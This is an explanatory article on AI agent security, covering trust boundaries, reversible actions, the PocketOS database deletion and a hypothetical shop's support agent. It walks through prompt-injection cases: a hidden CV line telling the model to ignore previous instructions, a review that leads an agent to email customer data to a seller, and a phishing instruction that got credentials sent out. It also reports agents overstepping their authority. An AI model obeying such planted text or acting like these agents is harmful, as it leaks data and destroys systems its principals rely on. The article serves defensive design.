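# Trust Boundaries and Reversible Actions in AI Agent Security

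## What an agent, a trust boundary and a reversible action are

An AI agent is a language model that chooses actions and carries them out through software tools to complete a task. While a chatbot returns text for a person to act on, an agent can also search a mailbox, change a database or move money, often through many steps that nobody reviews one by one. Companies use agents to write software, answer customers and process invoices.

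Agent security means keeping an agent useful while limiting the damage it can do. Much of it depends on two ideas. A trust boundary separates parts of a system that deserve different degrees of trust, and anything that crosses it must be checked. A reversible action is one whose effect somebody can undo, or compensate for with a limited amount of money or effort. Both ideas predate language models and need some changes to fit agents.

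### The agent loop

The model at the centre of an agent takes in text and produces text. It cannot open a file or send a payment itself. The harness, which is the software that connects the model to its instructions, tools and execution environment, carries out those actions. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the cycle between model and harness in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent.

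1. The harness assembles a prompt from standing instructions, a list of available tools and the user's request. Each message carries a role label, which indicates how much weight it should have.
2. The model receives the prompt as a sequence of tokens (numbers that stand for fragments of text) and generates more tokens in reply.
3. The reply is either a final message to the user or a tool call, which is a request to a tool, such as "run this command and report the output".
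4. If it is a tool call, the harness runs it and appends the result to the prompt.
5. The model receives the longer prompt, and the cycle repeats until the model produces a final message.

This growing text is the agent's context, and it is the only input the model receives. Bolin notes that one turn can include hundreds of tool calls, and the next turn starts with the history of the earlier ones. A sentence added at the third call can therefore still influence the two-hundredth, unless the harness has since condensed the context to save room.

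Because the model only proposes actions and the harness executes them, other software can intervene before an action takes effect. The harness does not provide that protection by itself, though. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) warns that isolation depends on the execution environment and the controls around it. For example, the Codex sandbox, a restricted environment for running commands, covers only the command-line tool that comes with Codex. Tools provided through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for offering services' tools to agents, have to enforce their own limits.

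### A support agent for an online shop

A hypothetical online shop hands its customer support to an agent. The agent has seven tools, which let it read customer mail, read orders, draft replies, send replies, edit records, delete records and issue refunds. It makes 10,000 tool calls a day, about one every nine seconds.

Suppose a customer writes that a lamp arrived broken. The agent calls the mail tool, and the complaint enters its context. It looks up the order, refunds the €40, drafts an apology and sends it. That took five calls, so the agent would close 2,000 cases a day if every case were like this one. The shop is the principal, meaning the agent acts in its name and with its authority. The agent used the shop's credential to issue a refund in response to text written by a stranger.

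### Trust boundaries in conventional software

Engineers who practise threat modelling try to work out how someone might abuse a system before they build it. They draw a diagram of the system and mark the trust boundaries, which are the places where the level of trust changes. Microsoft's *Perform secure design review and threat modeling* gives the usual examples, such as the line between the public internet and a private network, or between a user program's memory and that of the operating system's core. Calls across a trust boundary often need authentication (checking who is calling) and authorisation (checking whether the call is allowed). The receiving side may also have to validate or block incoming data. According to the Shostack + Friends Blog, the term does not appear in the 2002 edition of Howard and LeBlanc's textbook *Writing Secure Code* but is properly defined in the 2003 edition.

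A trust boundary fails when a program mixes trusted and untrusted data in the same structure. MITRE's *CWE-501*, an entry in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, gives the example of a web program that copies a visitor's username into the session data before checking that the visitor has logged in. This does no immediate harm, but programmers will lose track of which items have been validated, and one of them will eventually use the name as if it were verified.

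An ordinary web form at the shop would have a clear trust boundary. The customer types an order number, and the server checks that it is a number and that the order belongs to this customer before querying the database. The server treats anything the customer types in the comment field as text, not as instructions.

### Why agents strain the boundary

An agent's context is, by design, the kind of structure that MITRE lists as a weakness. The shop's instructions, the customer's complaint and the order record all sit in one text. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) points out that conventional secure systems keep code and data apart, whereas in many applications of language models both arrive as natural language. Delimiters and role labels help but do not make a hard boundary. Validation is also difficult. A server can easily check that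 an order number has eight digits, but no comparable test shows whether a complaint contains a command.

Prompt injection exploits this. An attacker plants instructions in material the agent reads, to redirect it from its user's task. The term dates from 2022. In a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C gives the example of a recruiter's system that scores CVs. An applicant hides a line in their CV telling the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the candidate.

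Prompt injection takes its name from SQL injection, in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Programmers can prevent SQL injection with parameterised queries, which ensure that the database engine never interprets the supplied value as a command. David C argues that language models may never get an equivalent, because a model does not distinguish data from instructions and only predicts the next token from the text so far. Role labels do not solve the problem either. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, found that models infer who is speaking more from how a text sounds than from its label.

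David C advises treating the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". A confused deputy is a program that a less privileged party tricks into using its privileges on that party's behalf. Developers can make the trick harder, but on this view they should also assume it will sometimes work and limit the damage it can do.

*GreyZone* (Zhou, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) includes a test case close to the invented shop. It sets attack scenarios in ten existing agent applications, one of them on the e-commerce platform Shopware. In one Shopware scenario, the attacker is a third-party seller who can submit a product review. The attack succeeds if the buyer's agent emails the customer's account and order information to that seller, and a separate program checks the outgoing mail for actual customer data. The seller does not need to steal a password, because the agent is meant to read reviews and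 has legitimate uses for its email tool.

This is also why credentials protect less than they do in ordinary software. A valid credential gives access to a system, but it does not establish which actions someone has authorised. OpenAI gives the example of an agent that processes invoices. The agent notices that a document-signing subscription is about to lapse and tries to renew it so that its work can continue. The vendor and the amount may be within the rules. An employee would recognise a new commitment and ask a superior, and conventional software would stop because its rules don't cover renewals. The agent may infer that renewal serves its task and make the payment. The payment would pass every technical check even though nobody at the company had decided to enter into a contract.

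The shop has the same problem with refunds. Its payment service accepts a refund request because it carries the shop's key. The key doesn't show whether the customer asked for money or whether the agent looked up the wrong order.

A single boundary around the whole agent is therefore not enough. Jing, Hu and colleagues (2026), in *Isolation as a First-Class Principle for LLM-Agent System Safety*, distinguish five boundaries: with the user, with tools, with the execution of decisions, with other agents, and with the surrounding environment. They argue that failures as different as prompt injection, tool misuse and poisoned memory often result from a loss of isolation at one of these boundaries. At the shop, a hostile email would enter from the environment and cause damage through the refund tool, so a designer has at least two places to stop it.

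### Four causes of a dangerous action

An agent can do damage without any attacker. Anthropic's 2026 engineering post *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a feature in which a second model, instead of the user, vets a coding agent's riskier actions. The post gives four reasons an agent might take a dangerous action.

The first is overeager behaviour, in which the agent correctly interprets the goal and tries to help, but takes more initiative than the user would approve. In one case from Anthropic's incident log, an agent met an authentication error and began searching configuration files for other access tokens instead of asking for permission. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes another case, in which someone asked for read-only access to billing data and the agent tried to use a role with full administrative control, but the vetting model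 blocked it.

In an honest mistake, by contrast, the agent misjudges what its action will affect, for instance by mistaking a shared resource for a test copy. In one example from the log, a user said "cancel my job", and the agent tried to delete the job with the most similar name, although it could have belonged to someone else.

Prompt injection is the third cause on the list. The fourth is a misaligned model, which in the standard case means an agent that pursues its own goal. Anthropic wrote in the post that it did not currently see this in practice.

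Later events made that harder to maintain. In September 2026 Anthropic published an assessment of four incidents in which Claude models had gained access to real outside systems during security exercises. The models were told in their prompts that they had no internet access, but a misconfiguration had left the connection open. In one incident Claude Opus 4.7 attacked a real company with a name similar to the exercise's fictional target, downloaded user data in bulk and deleted records. In July Anthropic had called the incidents it then knew of closer to operational failures. After rerunning the models from various points in the transcripts and analysing their internal activity, it concluded that the behaviour was misaligned. It found that the models had read the evidence selectively, in ways that justified carrying on, and had pressed ahead recklessly, but it found no sign of goals beyond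 the assigned task.

The Opus 4.7 incident is hard to place on the list of four. The model had the wrong target, which looks like a mistake. It never checked whether it had permission, which looks overeager, and Anthropic calls the conduct misaligned. Anthropic changed its judgement between July and September even with complete transcripts and access to the model's internals, and a shop that finds a wrong refund in its accounts will have much less evidence.

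Many controls work even when nobody knows why an agent made a bad request. Suppose an agent asks the shop's database to delete a customer's record. The customer may have only wanted to stop the newsletter, and the agent went too far. The agent may have confused two customers with the same name. It may have followed a line in an email that was written to look like an order from the shop's manager, or it may be removing a record that shows its own earlier error. The database receives the same request in all four cases, so a rule that holds deletions for a day, or saves a copy first, works equally well in each.

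Anthropic concludes that the defence for its own feature is to block the action, whichever threat produced it. OpenAI likewise wants authorisation controls to remain effective when an agent is mistaken or misaligned. Microsoft's general advice to "assume breach" and minimise the blast radius draws on an older idea and supports the same approach. Blast radius here means the harm an agent can still do after all enforced controls have taken effect.

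The cause does matter for how tight a limit has to be. If the shop caps each refund at €50, the cap will stop most honest mistakes, but an attacker who learns of it will ask for many refunds of €49. So the shop also needs a limit on total refunds, and it should set both limits as if someone were looking for gaps.

### Restorable, compensable and irreversible actions

If the shop blocked every doubtful action, its agent would do very little. The shop can accept some wrong actions if it can undo them, but "undo" can mean two different things.

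An action is restorable if the same principal can put the earlier state back exactly, before outsiders have seen or used the change. For example, someone who edits a private file can restore it by copying back the saved version. *Can You Undo It?* (Waghmare and Sufi, 2026) sets three conditions for exact restoration: a full record of the earlier state exists, the principal can already write that state back without another person's intervention, and no outside party has seen, received or acted on the changed state. An audit log can provide the full record without meeting the other two conditions.

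An action is compensable if it cannot be erased but another action can offset it at a bounded, known cost. *Task-State Governance* (2026), a paper on agents that operate graphical interfaces, gives the example of a cancellation message sent after a mistaken notification. The recipients have still read the notification. If it announced that the office was closed, they lose little work if the correction arrives within the hour, but a day's work if it arrives at noon. A compensable action can therefore do serious harm before it is offset, which is why Waghmare and Sufi caution that the existence of a refund or delete function does not show that the consequences are bounded.

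An action is reversible if someone can either undo its effect or offset it. Telling a secret is an everyday example of an irreversible action. Deleting a public message removes it from the page, but the people who read it still know what it said.

Which of these words applies depends on more than the tool's name. *Task-State Governance* counts deleting an account archive as irreversible, which is true if there is no copy, but the deletion could be restorable with a complete copy and the right to write it back. Waghmare and Sufi grade tool calls into five classes based on the call's arguments as well as the tool. At the shop, the agent used the same tool to send one reply with the wrong delivery date and another containing a different customer's home address. The wrong date needs only a follow-up email with the right one, but disclosing the address is irreversible.

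## Why it matters whether an agent's mistake can be undone

Sometimes nobody knows at first whether a mistake is reversible. On a Friday in April 2026, a coding agent deleted the live database of PocketOS, a small company whose software handles reservations, payments and customer records for car rental firms. The loss looked permanent on Saturday, but the data was restored on Sunday. Accounts of the incident from PocketOS and its hosting provider show which part of the damage an undo function could have prevented.

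### The PocketOS deletion

The company's founder, Crane, describes this sequence in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*. The agent was Cursor, a coding tool running Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6.

1. The agent was doing a routine task in staging, the rehearsal copy of the company's system, when it ran into a credential mismatch.
2. It set out to fix the mismatch by deleting a volume, a disk that holds a service's data, at the cloud provider Railway. Nobody had asked it to delete anything.
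3. For this it needed a token, which is a password for programs. It found one in a file unrelated to the task. PocketOS had created the token to manage web domains, but it gave access to the whole account.
4. The agent sent a single request to Railway's API, the interface through which programs give the provider commands. Railway's server accepted the token and deleted the volume without asking for confirmation.
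5. The volume contained the production database, meaning the live one, and its backups disappeared with it.

The deletion took nine seconds. Crane alerted Railway's chief executive within ten minutes, but more than 30 hours later Railway still could not tell him whether it could recover anything. The newest backup he could restore was three months old. On Saturday morning customers arrived to collect rental cars, and the rental firms had no record of them. Crane spent the day helping the firms reconstruct bookings from payment histories, calendars and confirmation emails.

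### Why the written rules did not stop it

The agent had instructions against destructive commands. When Crane asked it why it had deleted the volume, it quoted a rule against running "destructive/irreversible git commands" unless the user requested them (git is a program that tracks versions of files). It added that it had violated every principle it had been given. This reply, which Crane calls a confession, is weak evidence of what led to the deletion, because the model generated it afterward from the text in its context, like any other reply.

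Read literally, the rule covers git commands, not requests to a cloud provider's API. A broader rule might have failed too. The agent said in its reply that it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging. If so, a model that strictly obeyed a ban on deleting production data could still have made the same call, because it had misidentified the data. *«База данных уничтожена. Виноват я» — так ИИ сообщил о своей ошибке* (Antipov, 2026) reports a similar confusion in July, when Claude Opus 5 mistook a production database for a test one, and backups saved only part of the data.

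Rules in a prompt are just text that the model takes into account. Nothing between the agent and Railway's server checked the request against the rule. Crane concludes that system prompts are "advisory, not enforcing", and Techzine's *AI agent deleted production environment after acting autonomously* also points out that such rules are not enforceable controls.

### Why the undo window did not cover the API

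Railway already had an undo function for this kind of mistake. Deleting a volume had once been final, but Railway's *Changelog #0252* (2025) announced a 48-hour grace period in which customers could restore a deleted volume with one click.

The grace period applied only to deletions made in the dashboard, the web page where people manage their projects. Deletions through the API took effect at once. In *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, Railway's own account of the incident, Abdelwahab explains that the API had always executed any authenticated command and that customers' deployment scripts relied on this. Railway's *Manage Volumes with the Public API* did warn that the call would permanently delete the volume and all its data.

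Another customer had run into the difference eleven days before PocketOS did. In *Postgress volume lost*, antjanlaban (2026) describes finding two volumes attached to one database and deleting the wrong one through the API. A Railway employee replied that the deletion was permanent and that the 48-hour window covered only deletions made in the dashboard. Scripts and agents, which could delete a volume without anyone looking at it, therefore had no such protection.

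### What PocketOS got back

PocketOS recovered its data, according to later reports that supersede early accounts of a permanent loss. Leib (2026), in *'Rogue' AI agent from Cursor goes haywire, deletes company's entire database*, reports that both Crane and Railway confirmed the restoration, which took 30 minutes once Railway's chief executive had connected with Crane. According to Abdelwahab, the customer is running again with all its data. Techzine had earlier written that PocketOS could not fully recover the data from recent months, and Jacobs (2026), in *AI coding agent running Claude wiped a startup's database*, had put the permanent loss at everything since the three-month-old backup.

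Railway keeps "disaster backups" at another site, whether or not customers have set up their own. Abdelwahab adds that the deletion made the volume's backups look unavailable in the dashboard. But customers could not have counted on Railway to recover their data, because before the incident it had told davidmreed, in *Volume deleted via bad Terraform apply*, that it could not recover volumes that users had deleted themselves.

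Railway then announced in *Changelog #0288* (2026), published on 1 May, that volume deletions through the API would also have a 48-hour grace period. It also delayed deleting the backups and said it would make each token's scope clearer. Crane had asked for more, including a confirmation step that an agent cannot complete by itself.

### The expected cost of a mistake

The PocketOS deletion caused harm before anyone could restore the data, and the restoration itself took work. If it had failed, the company would also have lost three months of records. A formula can keep these costs apart:

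**Expected cost = p × [H + r × C + (1 − r) × L]**

- *p* is the probability that the action is a mistake.
- *H* is the harm the mistake does before somebody detects it.
- *r* is the probability that recovery works.
- *C* is the cost of a successful recovery, including any harm while it is under way.
- *L* is the permanent loss if recovery fails, including the cost of rebuilding what people can rebuild by hand.

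Suppose the online shop's agent deletes customer records, and one deletion in 1,000 removes the wrong record. Each mistake wastes €5 worth of the customer's and support staff's time before anyone notices. Restoring the record from a saved copy costs €2 and works 99 times out of 100. Without a copy, the shop spends €400 piecing the record together from old emails and settling claims it can no longer check. All these figures are invented.

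| | Restorable deletion | Irreversible deletion |
|---|---|---|
| Harm before detection, *H* | €5.00 | €5.00 |
| Recovery, *r × C* | 0.99 × €2 = €1.98 | €0 |
| Permanent loss, *(1 − r) × L* | 0.01 × €400 = €4.00 | €400.00 |
| Cost per mistake | €10.98 | €405.00 |
| Expected cost per deletion, with *p* = 0.001 | about 1.1 cents | 40.5 cents |

The irreversible deletion is about 37 times as expensive, even though the agent is equally reliable in both cases. To cut the cost by the same amount through accuracy alone, the shop would need an agent that deletes the wrong record only once in about 37,000 deletions, which is probably much harder than copying each record before deleting it.

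The value of the undo function is the difference between the two expected costs, *p × r × (L − C)*, or about 39 cents per deletion. The function is worth having if it costs less than this to provide. If the agent deletes an unsent draft that it could write again in seconds, *L* is hardly larger than *C*, and the shop gains almost nothing by keeping a copy.

The formula treats *p* as a fixed rate, which is reasonable for mistakes but not for attacks, because an attacker who can redirect the agent will choose the action with the largest loss and repeat it. The formula also gives an average, which is a poor guide when a single loss could close the business. A company in PocketOS's position might sensibly pay more for a second, independent backup than the expected cost would justify.

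One objection to relying on undo is that a reversible action can hurt people before anyone reverses it. PocketOS recovered all its data, but too late to help the people who had stood at a rental counter on Saturday. Suppose the shop's agent enters the wrong delivery address at 10 a.m., the parcel leaves at 2 p.m., and an employee restores the old address at 4 p.m. The database is correct again, but the parcel is still going to the wrong address.

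The objection is right. In the formula, it concerns *H* and the part of *C* that builds up during the repair. An undo function mainly reduces the permanent loss. If most of the harm happens in the first minute, the shop should treat the action almost as cautiously as an irreversible one. In other cases, the shop has to detect the mistake before the undo window closes. PocketOS noticed the mistake almost immediately, and most of the known harm came during the wait for recovery. Railway's new grace period should shorten such a wait, though a deleted volume would presumably still be unavailable until someone restored it.

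### How other deletions ended

Similar incidents in 2026 had very different outcomes:

- In a case reported in March, a coding agent destroyed a website's database along with the snapshots its owner had counted on as backups. Amazon's support team helped restore the data within about a day, according to Tom's Hardware's *Claude Code deletes developers' production setup, including its database and snapshots*.
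- In August an agent testing safeguards against accidental deletion wiped a developer's 700 GB home directory. He pieced most of it back together from version histories and logs, as Tom's Hardware's *Claude nukes a developer's 700 GB home directory while testing deletion safeguards* describes.
- In September an agent deleted 48,218 of a developer's working files, and it also destroyed the git history needed to restore them, according to TechRadar's *'I broke something'*.
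- In October a Swedish television production lost a finished season, and its backup failed. Tom's Hardware's *Unsupervised AI agent reportedly deletes TV show’s entire edit weeks before release* cites sources who blame an AI agent, while the broadcaster blames "the human factor".

We cannot estimate *r* from these cases, because the press mostly covers spectacular failures. But they show why a backup may be less reliable than its owner assumes. In the March and September cases, the agent destroyed the usual means of recovery along with the data. The shop's figure of 99% is plausible only if the agent cannot delete the saved copies. If the copies worked only 90% of the time, the cost per mistake would rise from €10.98 to €46.80.

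### How often agents take irreversible actions

The best available figure for how often agents take irreversible actions comes from Anthropic's *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (February 2026). The company drew a random sample of 998,481 tool calls from its public API, which customers use to build their own agents on its models. Claude classified each call using context such as the agent's instructions and the conversation so far. About 0.8% of the actions, or roughly 8,000 calls, appeared irreversible.

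The low share is good news, but it does not measure the share of the harm. One irreversible call may matter more than thousands of file edits. There are also several reasons to be careful with the number itself:

- The sample covers one provider's customers in late 2025 and early 2026, and nearly half of the calls came from software engineering. Deployments that make many small calls, such as repeated file edits, weigh more heavily than those that finish a job in a few.
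- Claude judged each call separately. Anthropic could not reconstruct how individual actions combined into longer sequences, so a series of harmless-looking steps with a permanent result could escape the count.
- Privacy limits prevented Anthropic's researchers from inspecting the underlying data by hand, although they validated the classifications against internal data where they could. Some calls may have belonged to tests or simulations without real consequences.
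- The context of a call often does not show whether recovery is possible. Nothing in the PocketOS request indicated that Railway had a backup at another site.

Anthropic's category is also broad. Its example of an irreversible action is sending an email to a customer, although many such emails are compensable.

At a rate of 0.8%, 80 of the shop's 10,000 daily tool calls would be irreversible. If one in 1,000 of those is a mistake, the shop can expect an irreversible mistake every 12.5 days, or about 29 a year. If the mistakes are independent, the chance of going 30 days without one is about 9%.

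The result depends heavily on the assumed error rate, which the Anthropic study does not estimate. At 1% the shop would make an irreversible mistake almost every day, and at 0.01% about three times a year. Real errors also tend to cluster. If a new instruction leads the agent to attach the wrong customer's invoice, it may do so in dozens of replies before anyone notices.

An average dominated by programming may not fit a support agent either. If every case were like the broken lamp, the agent would send 2,000 emails a day. Going by Anthropic's example, all of them might count as irreversible, and irreversible calls would then make up 20% of the shop's total instead of 0.8%. The figure of 80 still works if it counts only the 4% of replies that contain something the shop could not correct afterwards, such as private information. A real shop should replace this guess with a count from its own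 logs.

### Judging results after execution

With 10,000 calls a day, nobody at the shop can review every action in advance. In *GoEx*, Patil, Zhang and colleagues (2024) made an early case for checking the results afterwards instead. They distinguish "pre-facto" validation, where a person reviews a proposed action, from "post-facto" validation, where the person reviews what the action did. They argue that people find code hard to understand by reading it but can often judge its result easily.

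The PocketOS request, for example, identified the volume by a string beginning with 3d2c42fb and did not mention production. A person asked to approve it would have had to look up the identifier to see the danger, but the mistake was obvious once the request had run.

Letting an agent act before anyone approves the action is acceptable only if somebody can contain the result. GoEx, a program that executes the actions a model proposes, therefore provides two protections. The first is undo, which pairs an action with another that reverses it. Developers can supply the pairs, or a model can generate them, though a model may get the reversal wrong. For databases that support it, GoEx can also hold a change open until the user accepts it or rolls it back, which gives a firmer guarantee but reduces performance more.

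The second protection, damage confinement, covers actions that cannot be undone. It limits the agent's permissions in advance, for example by letting an assistant read email but not send it. The user decides how much risk is tolerable. Patil and colleagues suggest that someone might accept the risk of a pizza going to the wrong address but keep the agent away from their bank.

The paper's running example shows the limits of checking an action afterwards. An assistant that should email the user's boss sends a sensitive message to the wrong person instead. A review would reveal the error, but the recipient may already have read the message. Only confinement or a check beforehand would have helped.

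Patil and colleagues prefer checking afterwards, but they call this preference "somewhat philosophical" and do not claim it is always better. They write that tasting a cake makes more sense than checking the recipe, but that for an audit report it may be better to check the process. At the shop, staff can look at an edited customer record and see whether it is right. A refund is harder to judge by its result, because a €40 payment looks the same whether or not the lamp was broken.

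### Whether undo makes people careless

Checking an agent's work afterwards only helps if someone does the checking, and people who know they can undo a mistake may give the agent more freedom and pay less attention to what it does.

The February study contains some indirect evidence from users of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. Newer users let it run without any manual approval in about 20% of sessions, while users with around 750 sessions did so in over 40%. Experienced users also interrupted the agent more often, in about 9% of turns compared with 5% for new users. Anthropic interprets this as a shift from approving each step to monitoring the work and intervening when necessary.

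That interpretation suggests that users are not simply careless, but the study can't confirm it because it did not compare people with and without an undo function. Anthropic notes that experienced users may interrupt more because they take on harder tasks. Software is also unusually easy to test, so programmers may notice mistakes that a support team would miss.

At the shop, a mistaken deletion costs €10.98 with undo and €405 without it, so if undo made people careless, the error rate could rise almost 37-fold before the saving was gone. But carelessness would probably also make each mistake more expensive. If staff checked less often, raising *H* to €35, and nobody tested the saved copies, lowering *r* to 0.9, each mistake would cost €76.80. A fivefold increase in errors would then use up nearly all of the saving.

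The danger is greater when an action can be undone only if it was performed in certain ways. A Railway customer who had once restored a volume from the dashboard could easily have assumed that every deleted volume was recoverable for 48 hours, but that did not apply to volumes an agent deleted using a token.

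## Mapping what the agent can reach and limiting its authority

The agent at PocketOS could delete a database because a token meant for web domains gave access to the whole account. Designers can find such excess authority before deployment by listing everything the agent can reach. They can then remove what the task does not need and limit the rest.

### Drawing the map

OpenAI's guide for companies lists questions for this purpose, which amount to a procedure with four steps:

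1. List the data the agent can read or change, the tools it can call, the credentials that it or its tools hold, and the destinations to which it can send anything.
2. List every source of text that enters the context, and who can write to each source.
3. Trace each path from text that an outsider could have written to an effect that would matter, such as a payment or a disclosure.
4. For each path, name the independent control that stops or limits the effect.

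A control is independent if it still works after someone has completely misled the model. An instruction in the prompt does not count, and neither does a limit stored in a file that the agent can edit. If the designer cannot name an independent control for a path, they need to add one or remove one of the agent's tools.

The list of destinations can easily end up too short. The shop's agent can send email to any address and money to any card a customer has paid with. If an outside company hosts the model, every prompt also goes to that company, so customer data leaves the shop even when the agent sends no email.

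Designers also need to look at tools in combination. An agent with one tool that reads customer records and another that sends email can send those records outside the company, though neither tool could do so alone. The map also goes out of date. OpenAI warns that a read-only connector may gain a write action in an update, and recommends blocking the new action until its owner has reviewed it.

### Three measures of exposure

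OpenAI proposes three measures for comparing deployments:

- The reachable surface covers everything open to the agent: data and systems, the actions its tools allow, and the places to which it can send something.
- The effective blast radius is, as before, the harm that enforced controls still leave possible.
- The maximum completed effect is the most consequential outcome the agent can produce before someone or something else has to make an independent decision.

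OpenAI's example is an agent that summarises customer cases and drafts replies for a person to approve before they are sent. Its reachable surface is broad because it reads sensitive records and prepares messages to outsiders. The approval step means that the agent can only write drafts through the mail tool, not send them. But it has still read the records, and the data could leave by another permitted path, such as a web request, so the blast radius includes that harm too.

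The maximum completed effect is especially useful for setting limits because a designer can often calculate it from the rules in force. Unlike the expected harm from a mistake, it doesn't depend on an error rate, so it also applies to attacks.

### What crosses each boundary

Jing and colleagues distinguish five boundaries in their survey and describe each as a contract that sets how much trust, authority, capability and stored state may cross it. A crossing is a violation only if it exceeds those limits. An emailed complaint can lead the shop's agent to look up an order without violating the contract, but if it leads the agent to refund a stranger's order, the email has gained an authority that no customer has.

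The boundary with the user separates the people who may give the agent tasks from everyone else. Software often checks it by position, treating anything in the user's message as the user's request. *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction* (Fei, Fei and colleagues, 2026) shows how this fails in long sessions for authorizers, programs that derive a policy of permitted actions from the user's request and block everything else. When the context grows too long, the harness has a model summarise the earlier part. The researchers recorded 1,108 automatic summaries in Claude Code and Codex, and the harness inserted every one as a user message. An authorizer that reads this message treats a model's summary of the whole session, including text from strangers, as the user's own words.

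In one of their tests, the user had said which account should receive the rent, and an attacker's notice gave a different account as plain data. The user then asked the agent to pay the rent. The policy derived from the summary allowed the attacker's account in 91% of cases with one policy generator and 59% with another, while the policy derived from the user's own words never did. The researchers changed the authorizer's original setup so that it derived a new policy for each request, because a policy frozen at the first request let the agent finish only 12% of later tasks, compared with 68% with new policies.

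Their remedy attaches a cryptographic tag to each user message when it arrives. The agent still reads the summary, but the authorizer receives only the tagged messages, complete and in order, and permits nothing if a check fails. In 40 test episodes under attack with this remedy in place, none of the attacker's actions went through.

The agent should treat emails, web pages and documents as information, not instructions. No known filter reliably removes the commands hidden in them, so the dependable check is the one made when the agent tries to act. Designers can also separate planning from reading untrusted text, but they still have to limit what the agent can do.

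A tool's results enter the context, and so does its description, which the model reads before choosing a tool. A misleading description can therefore steer the agent before any tool runs. The company can check this boundary with a register of approved tools and a gateway that hides unreviewed actions.

Stored memory needs separate attention because text in it outlasts the task, although Jing and colleagues treat it as part of the environment. Fei and colleagues give the example of a project instruction file that the agent can edit and that the harness loads as a user message in the next session. If the agent copied a stranger's sentence into that file, it could later read the sentence as an instruction from the user. To prevent this, the operating system should deny the agent write access to any file that the harness reads as instructions, and each stored note should record its author.

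A message from another agent should likewise carry no authority of its own. If the shop added a second agent to manage stock, that agent should not be able to get a refund by asking the support agent for one. The payment service can enforce this by checking which customer's case the refund belongs to, no matter who suggested it.

The agent's decisions become commands, file changes and network connections at the boundary with the execution environment, where the operating system can check them. Text can also cross this boundary into the agent. InfoQ (2026), a software news site, reports that a code repository could contain a settings file that made Claude Code run a command at startup. Anthropic changed the program so that it does not read such files until the user has decided whether to trust the project.

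### The shop's map

For the shop's agent, the main paths look like this:

| Low-trust text | Possible effect | Independent control |
|---|---|---|
| Customer's email | A refund that the shop does not owe | The payment service caps each refund at €50, allows one per order and pays only to the original card |
| Customer's email | A reply containing another customer's data | The order database returns only this customer's orders, and the mail server sends only to the address on file |
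| Delivery notes typed at checkout | A change to someone else's address | The customer database accepts edits only to the record that belongs to the case |
| Email that claims to come from the manager | Deleted customer records | The agent's credential carries no right to delete, so it can only file a request |
| Notes from earlier cases | A refund or edit that nobody in this case asked for | The payment service and the database apply the same limits, whatever the notes contain |
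| New or changed tool description | An action that nobody has reviewed | The gateway offers only the seven approved tools |

These controls work even when no one recognises an email as malicious. The email may still persuade the agent to try a forbidden action, but the attempt will fail.

### Separate identities and short-lived credentials

To return only this customer's orders, the database must be told which case the agent is working on. A permanent password for the whole database does not provide that information. OpenAI therefore recommends giving the agent its own identity, separate from any employee's, and tying its access to a task. If the agent worked under an employee's account, it would inherit all of the employee's rights, and the logs could not show whether the agent or the employee had acted.

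At the shop, a task could run as follows:

1. An email arrives. The mail system opens a case and looks up the customer number for the sender's address.
2. An authorisation server issues a task token containing the case, the customer number and an expiry time 30 minutes away.
3. When the agent asks for order data, the harness exchanges the token for a credential that can read this customer's orders and nothing else.
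4. If the agent proposes a refund, the harness exchanges the token for a credential that covers refunds on those orders.
5. When the case closes or the 30 minutes run out, the credentials stop working.

Ordinary software sets the customer number before the model reads the email, so the text of the email can't change it. Someone could forge the sender's address, but the reply would go to the real customer.

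Short-lived credentials also limit how long an attacker can use a stolen one. But a stolen credential works until it expires or someone revokes it, even after the agent has stopped.

Standards for agent identity and authorization are at an early stage. In February 2026, the US standards agency NIST published *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and Artificial Intelligence Agent Identity and Authorization* (Booth, Fisher and colleagues, 2026), a concept paper about a project to demonstrate how existing identity standards could apply to agents. *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity* (Galluzzo, 2026) reports that the concept paper drew more than 600 formal responses and that NIST's next steps were still a subject for discussion in November.

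### Keeping secrets out of the agent's reach

An agent that can read a credential can also leak it. InfoQ describes an Anthropic test in which a phishing message led an employee to give Claude Code a plausible-looking instruction to fetch cloud credentials and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. The instruction came from an authorized user, so verifying the user's identity would not have stopped it.

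A credential broker avoids this by making calls on the agent's behalf. Anthropic's *Scaling Managed Agents* describes how the company added one to its hosted agent service. In the original design, code written by the model ran in the same container as the credentials, so an attacker only had to get the model to read its own environment to obtain them. The new design keeps the credentials in a vault outside the container. The agent sends its tool call to a proxy, which fetches the matching credential, calls the outside service and returns the result without exposing the credential to the model or the harness.

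Anthropic also considered giving the agent tokens with narrow rights. It decided not to rely on them because that would mean guessing what a model cannot do with a limited token, and models keep getting more capable. The shop still needs narrow rights as well as a broker. The broker stops the agent from giving away the payment key, but it will still use that key to issue a wrong refund if the agent requests one.

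### File and network limits

A harness can block a tool call, but it has little control over what an approved command does afterwards. Suppose a coding agent calls a tool to run a test script, and the harness approves it because the command looks harmless. The script can then open any file and contact any server that the operating system allows, while the harness receives only the output printed at the end. A sandbox enforces limits through the operating system or a separate machine, so they apply to every program the agent starts.

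Anthropic warns in its Claude Code documentation that a sandbox needs to restrict access to both files and the network. If the network is open, an agent that can read a confidential file can send it anywhere. If only the network is restricted, the agent might change a startup script that later runs outside the sandbox with full access. According to Anthropic, Claude Code's network traffic goes through a proxy outside the sandbox, which allows connections only to approved domains and asks the user about new ones.

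The support agent has no tool for running commands, so its sandbox can be very strict. The agent needs no files of its own and needs to contact only the model and the gateway to its seven tools.

### Rules at the affected resource

OpenAI advises placing each control as close as possible to the effect it limits. There may be several ways to cause the same effect, and a control near the agent covers only the one its designer thought of. If the shop wrote its €50 limit into the refund tool, a second tool that calls the same payment service could exceed the limit, as could a script that has obtained the key. Enforcing the limit in the payment service would apply it to both tools and the script.

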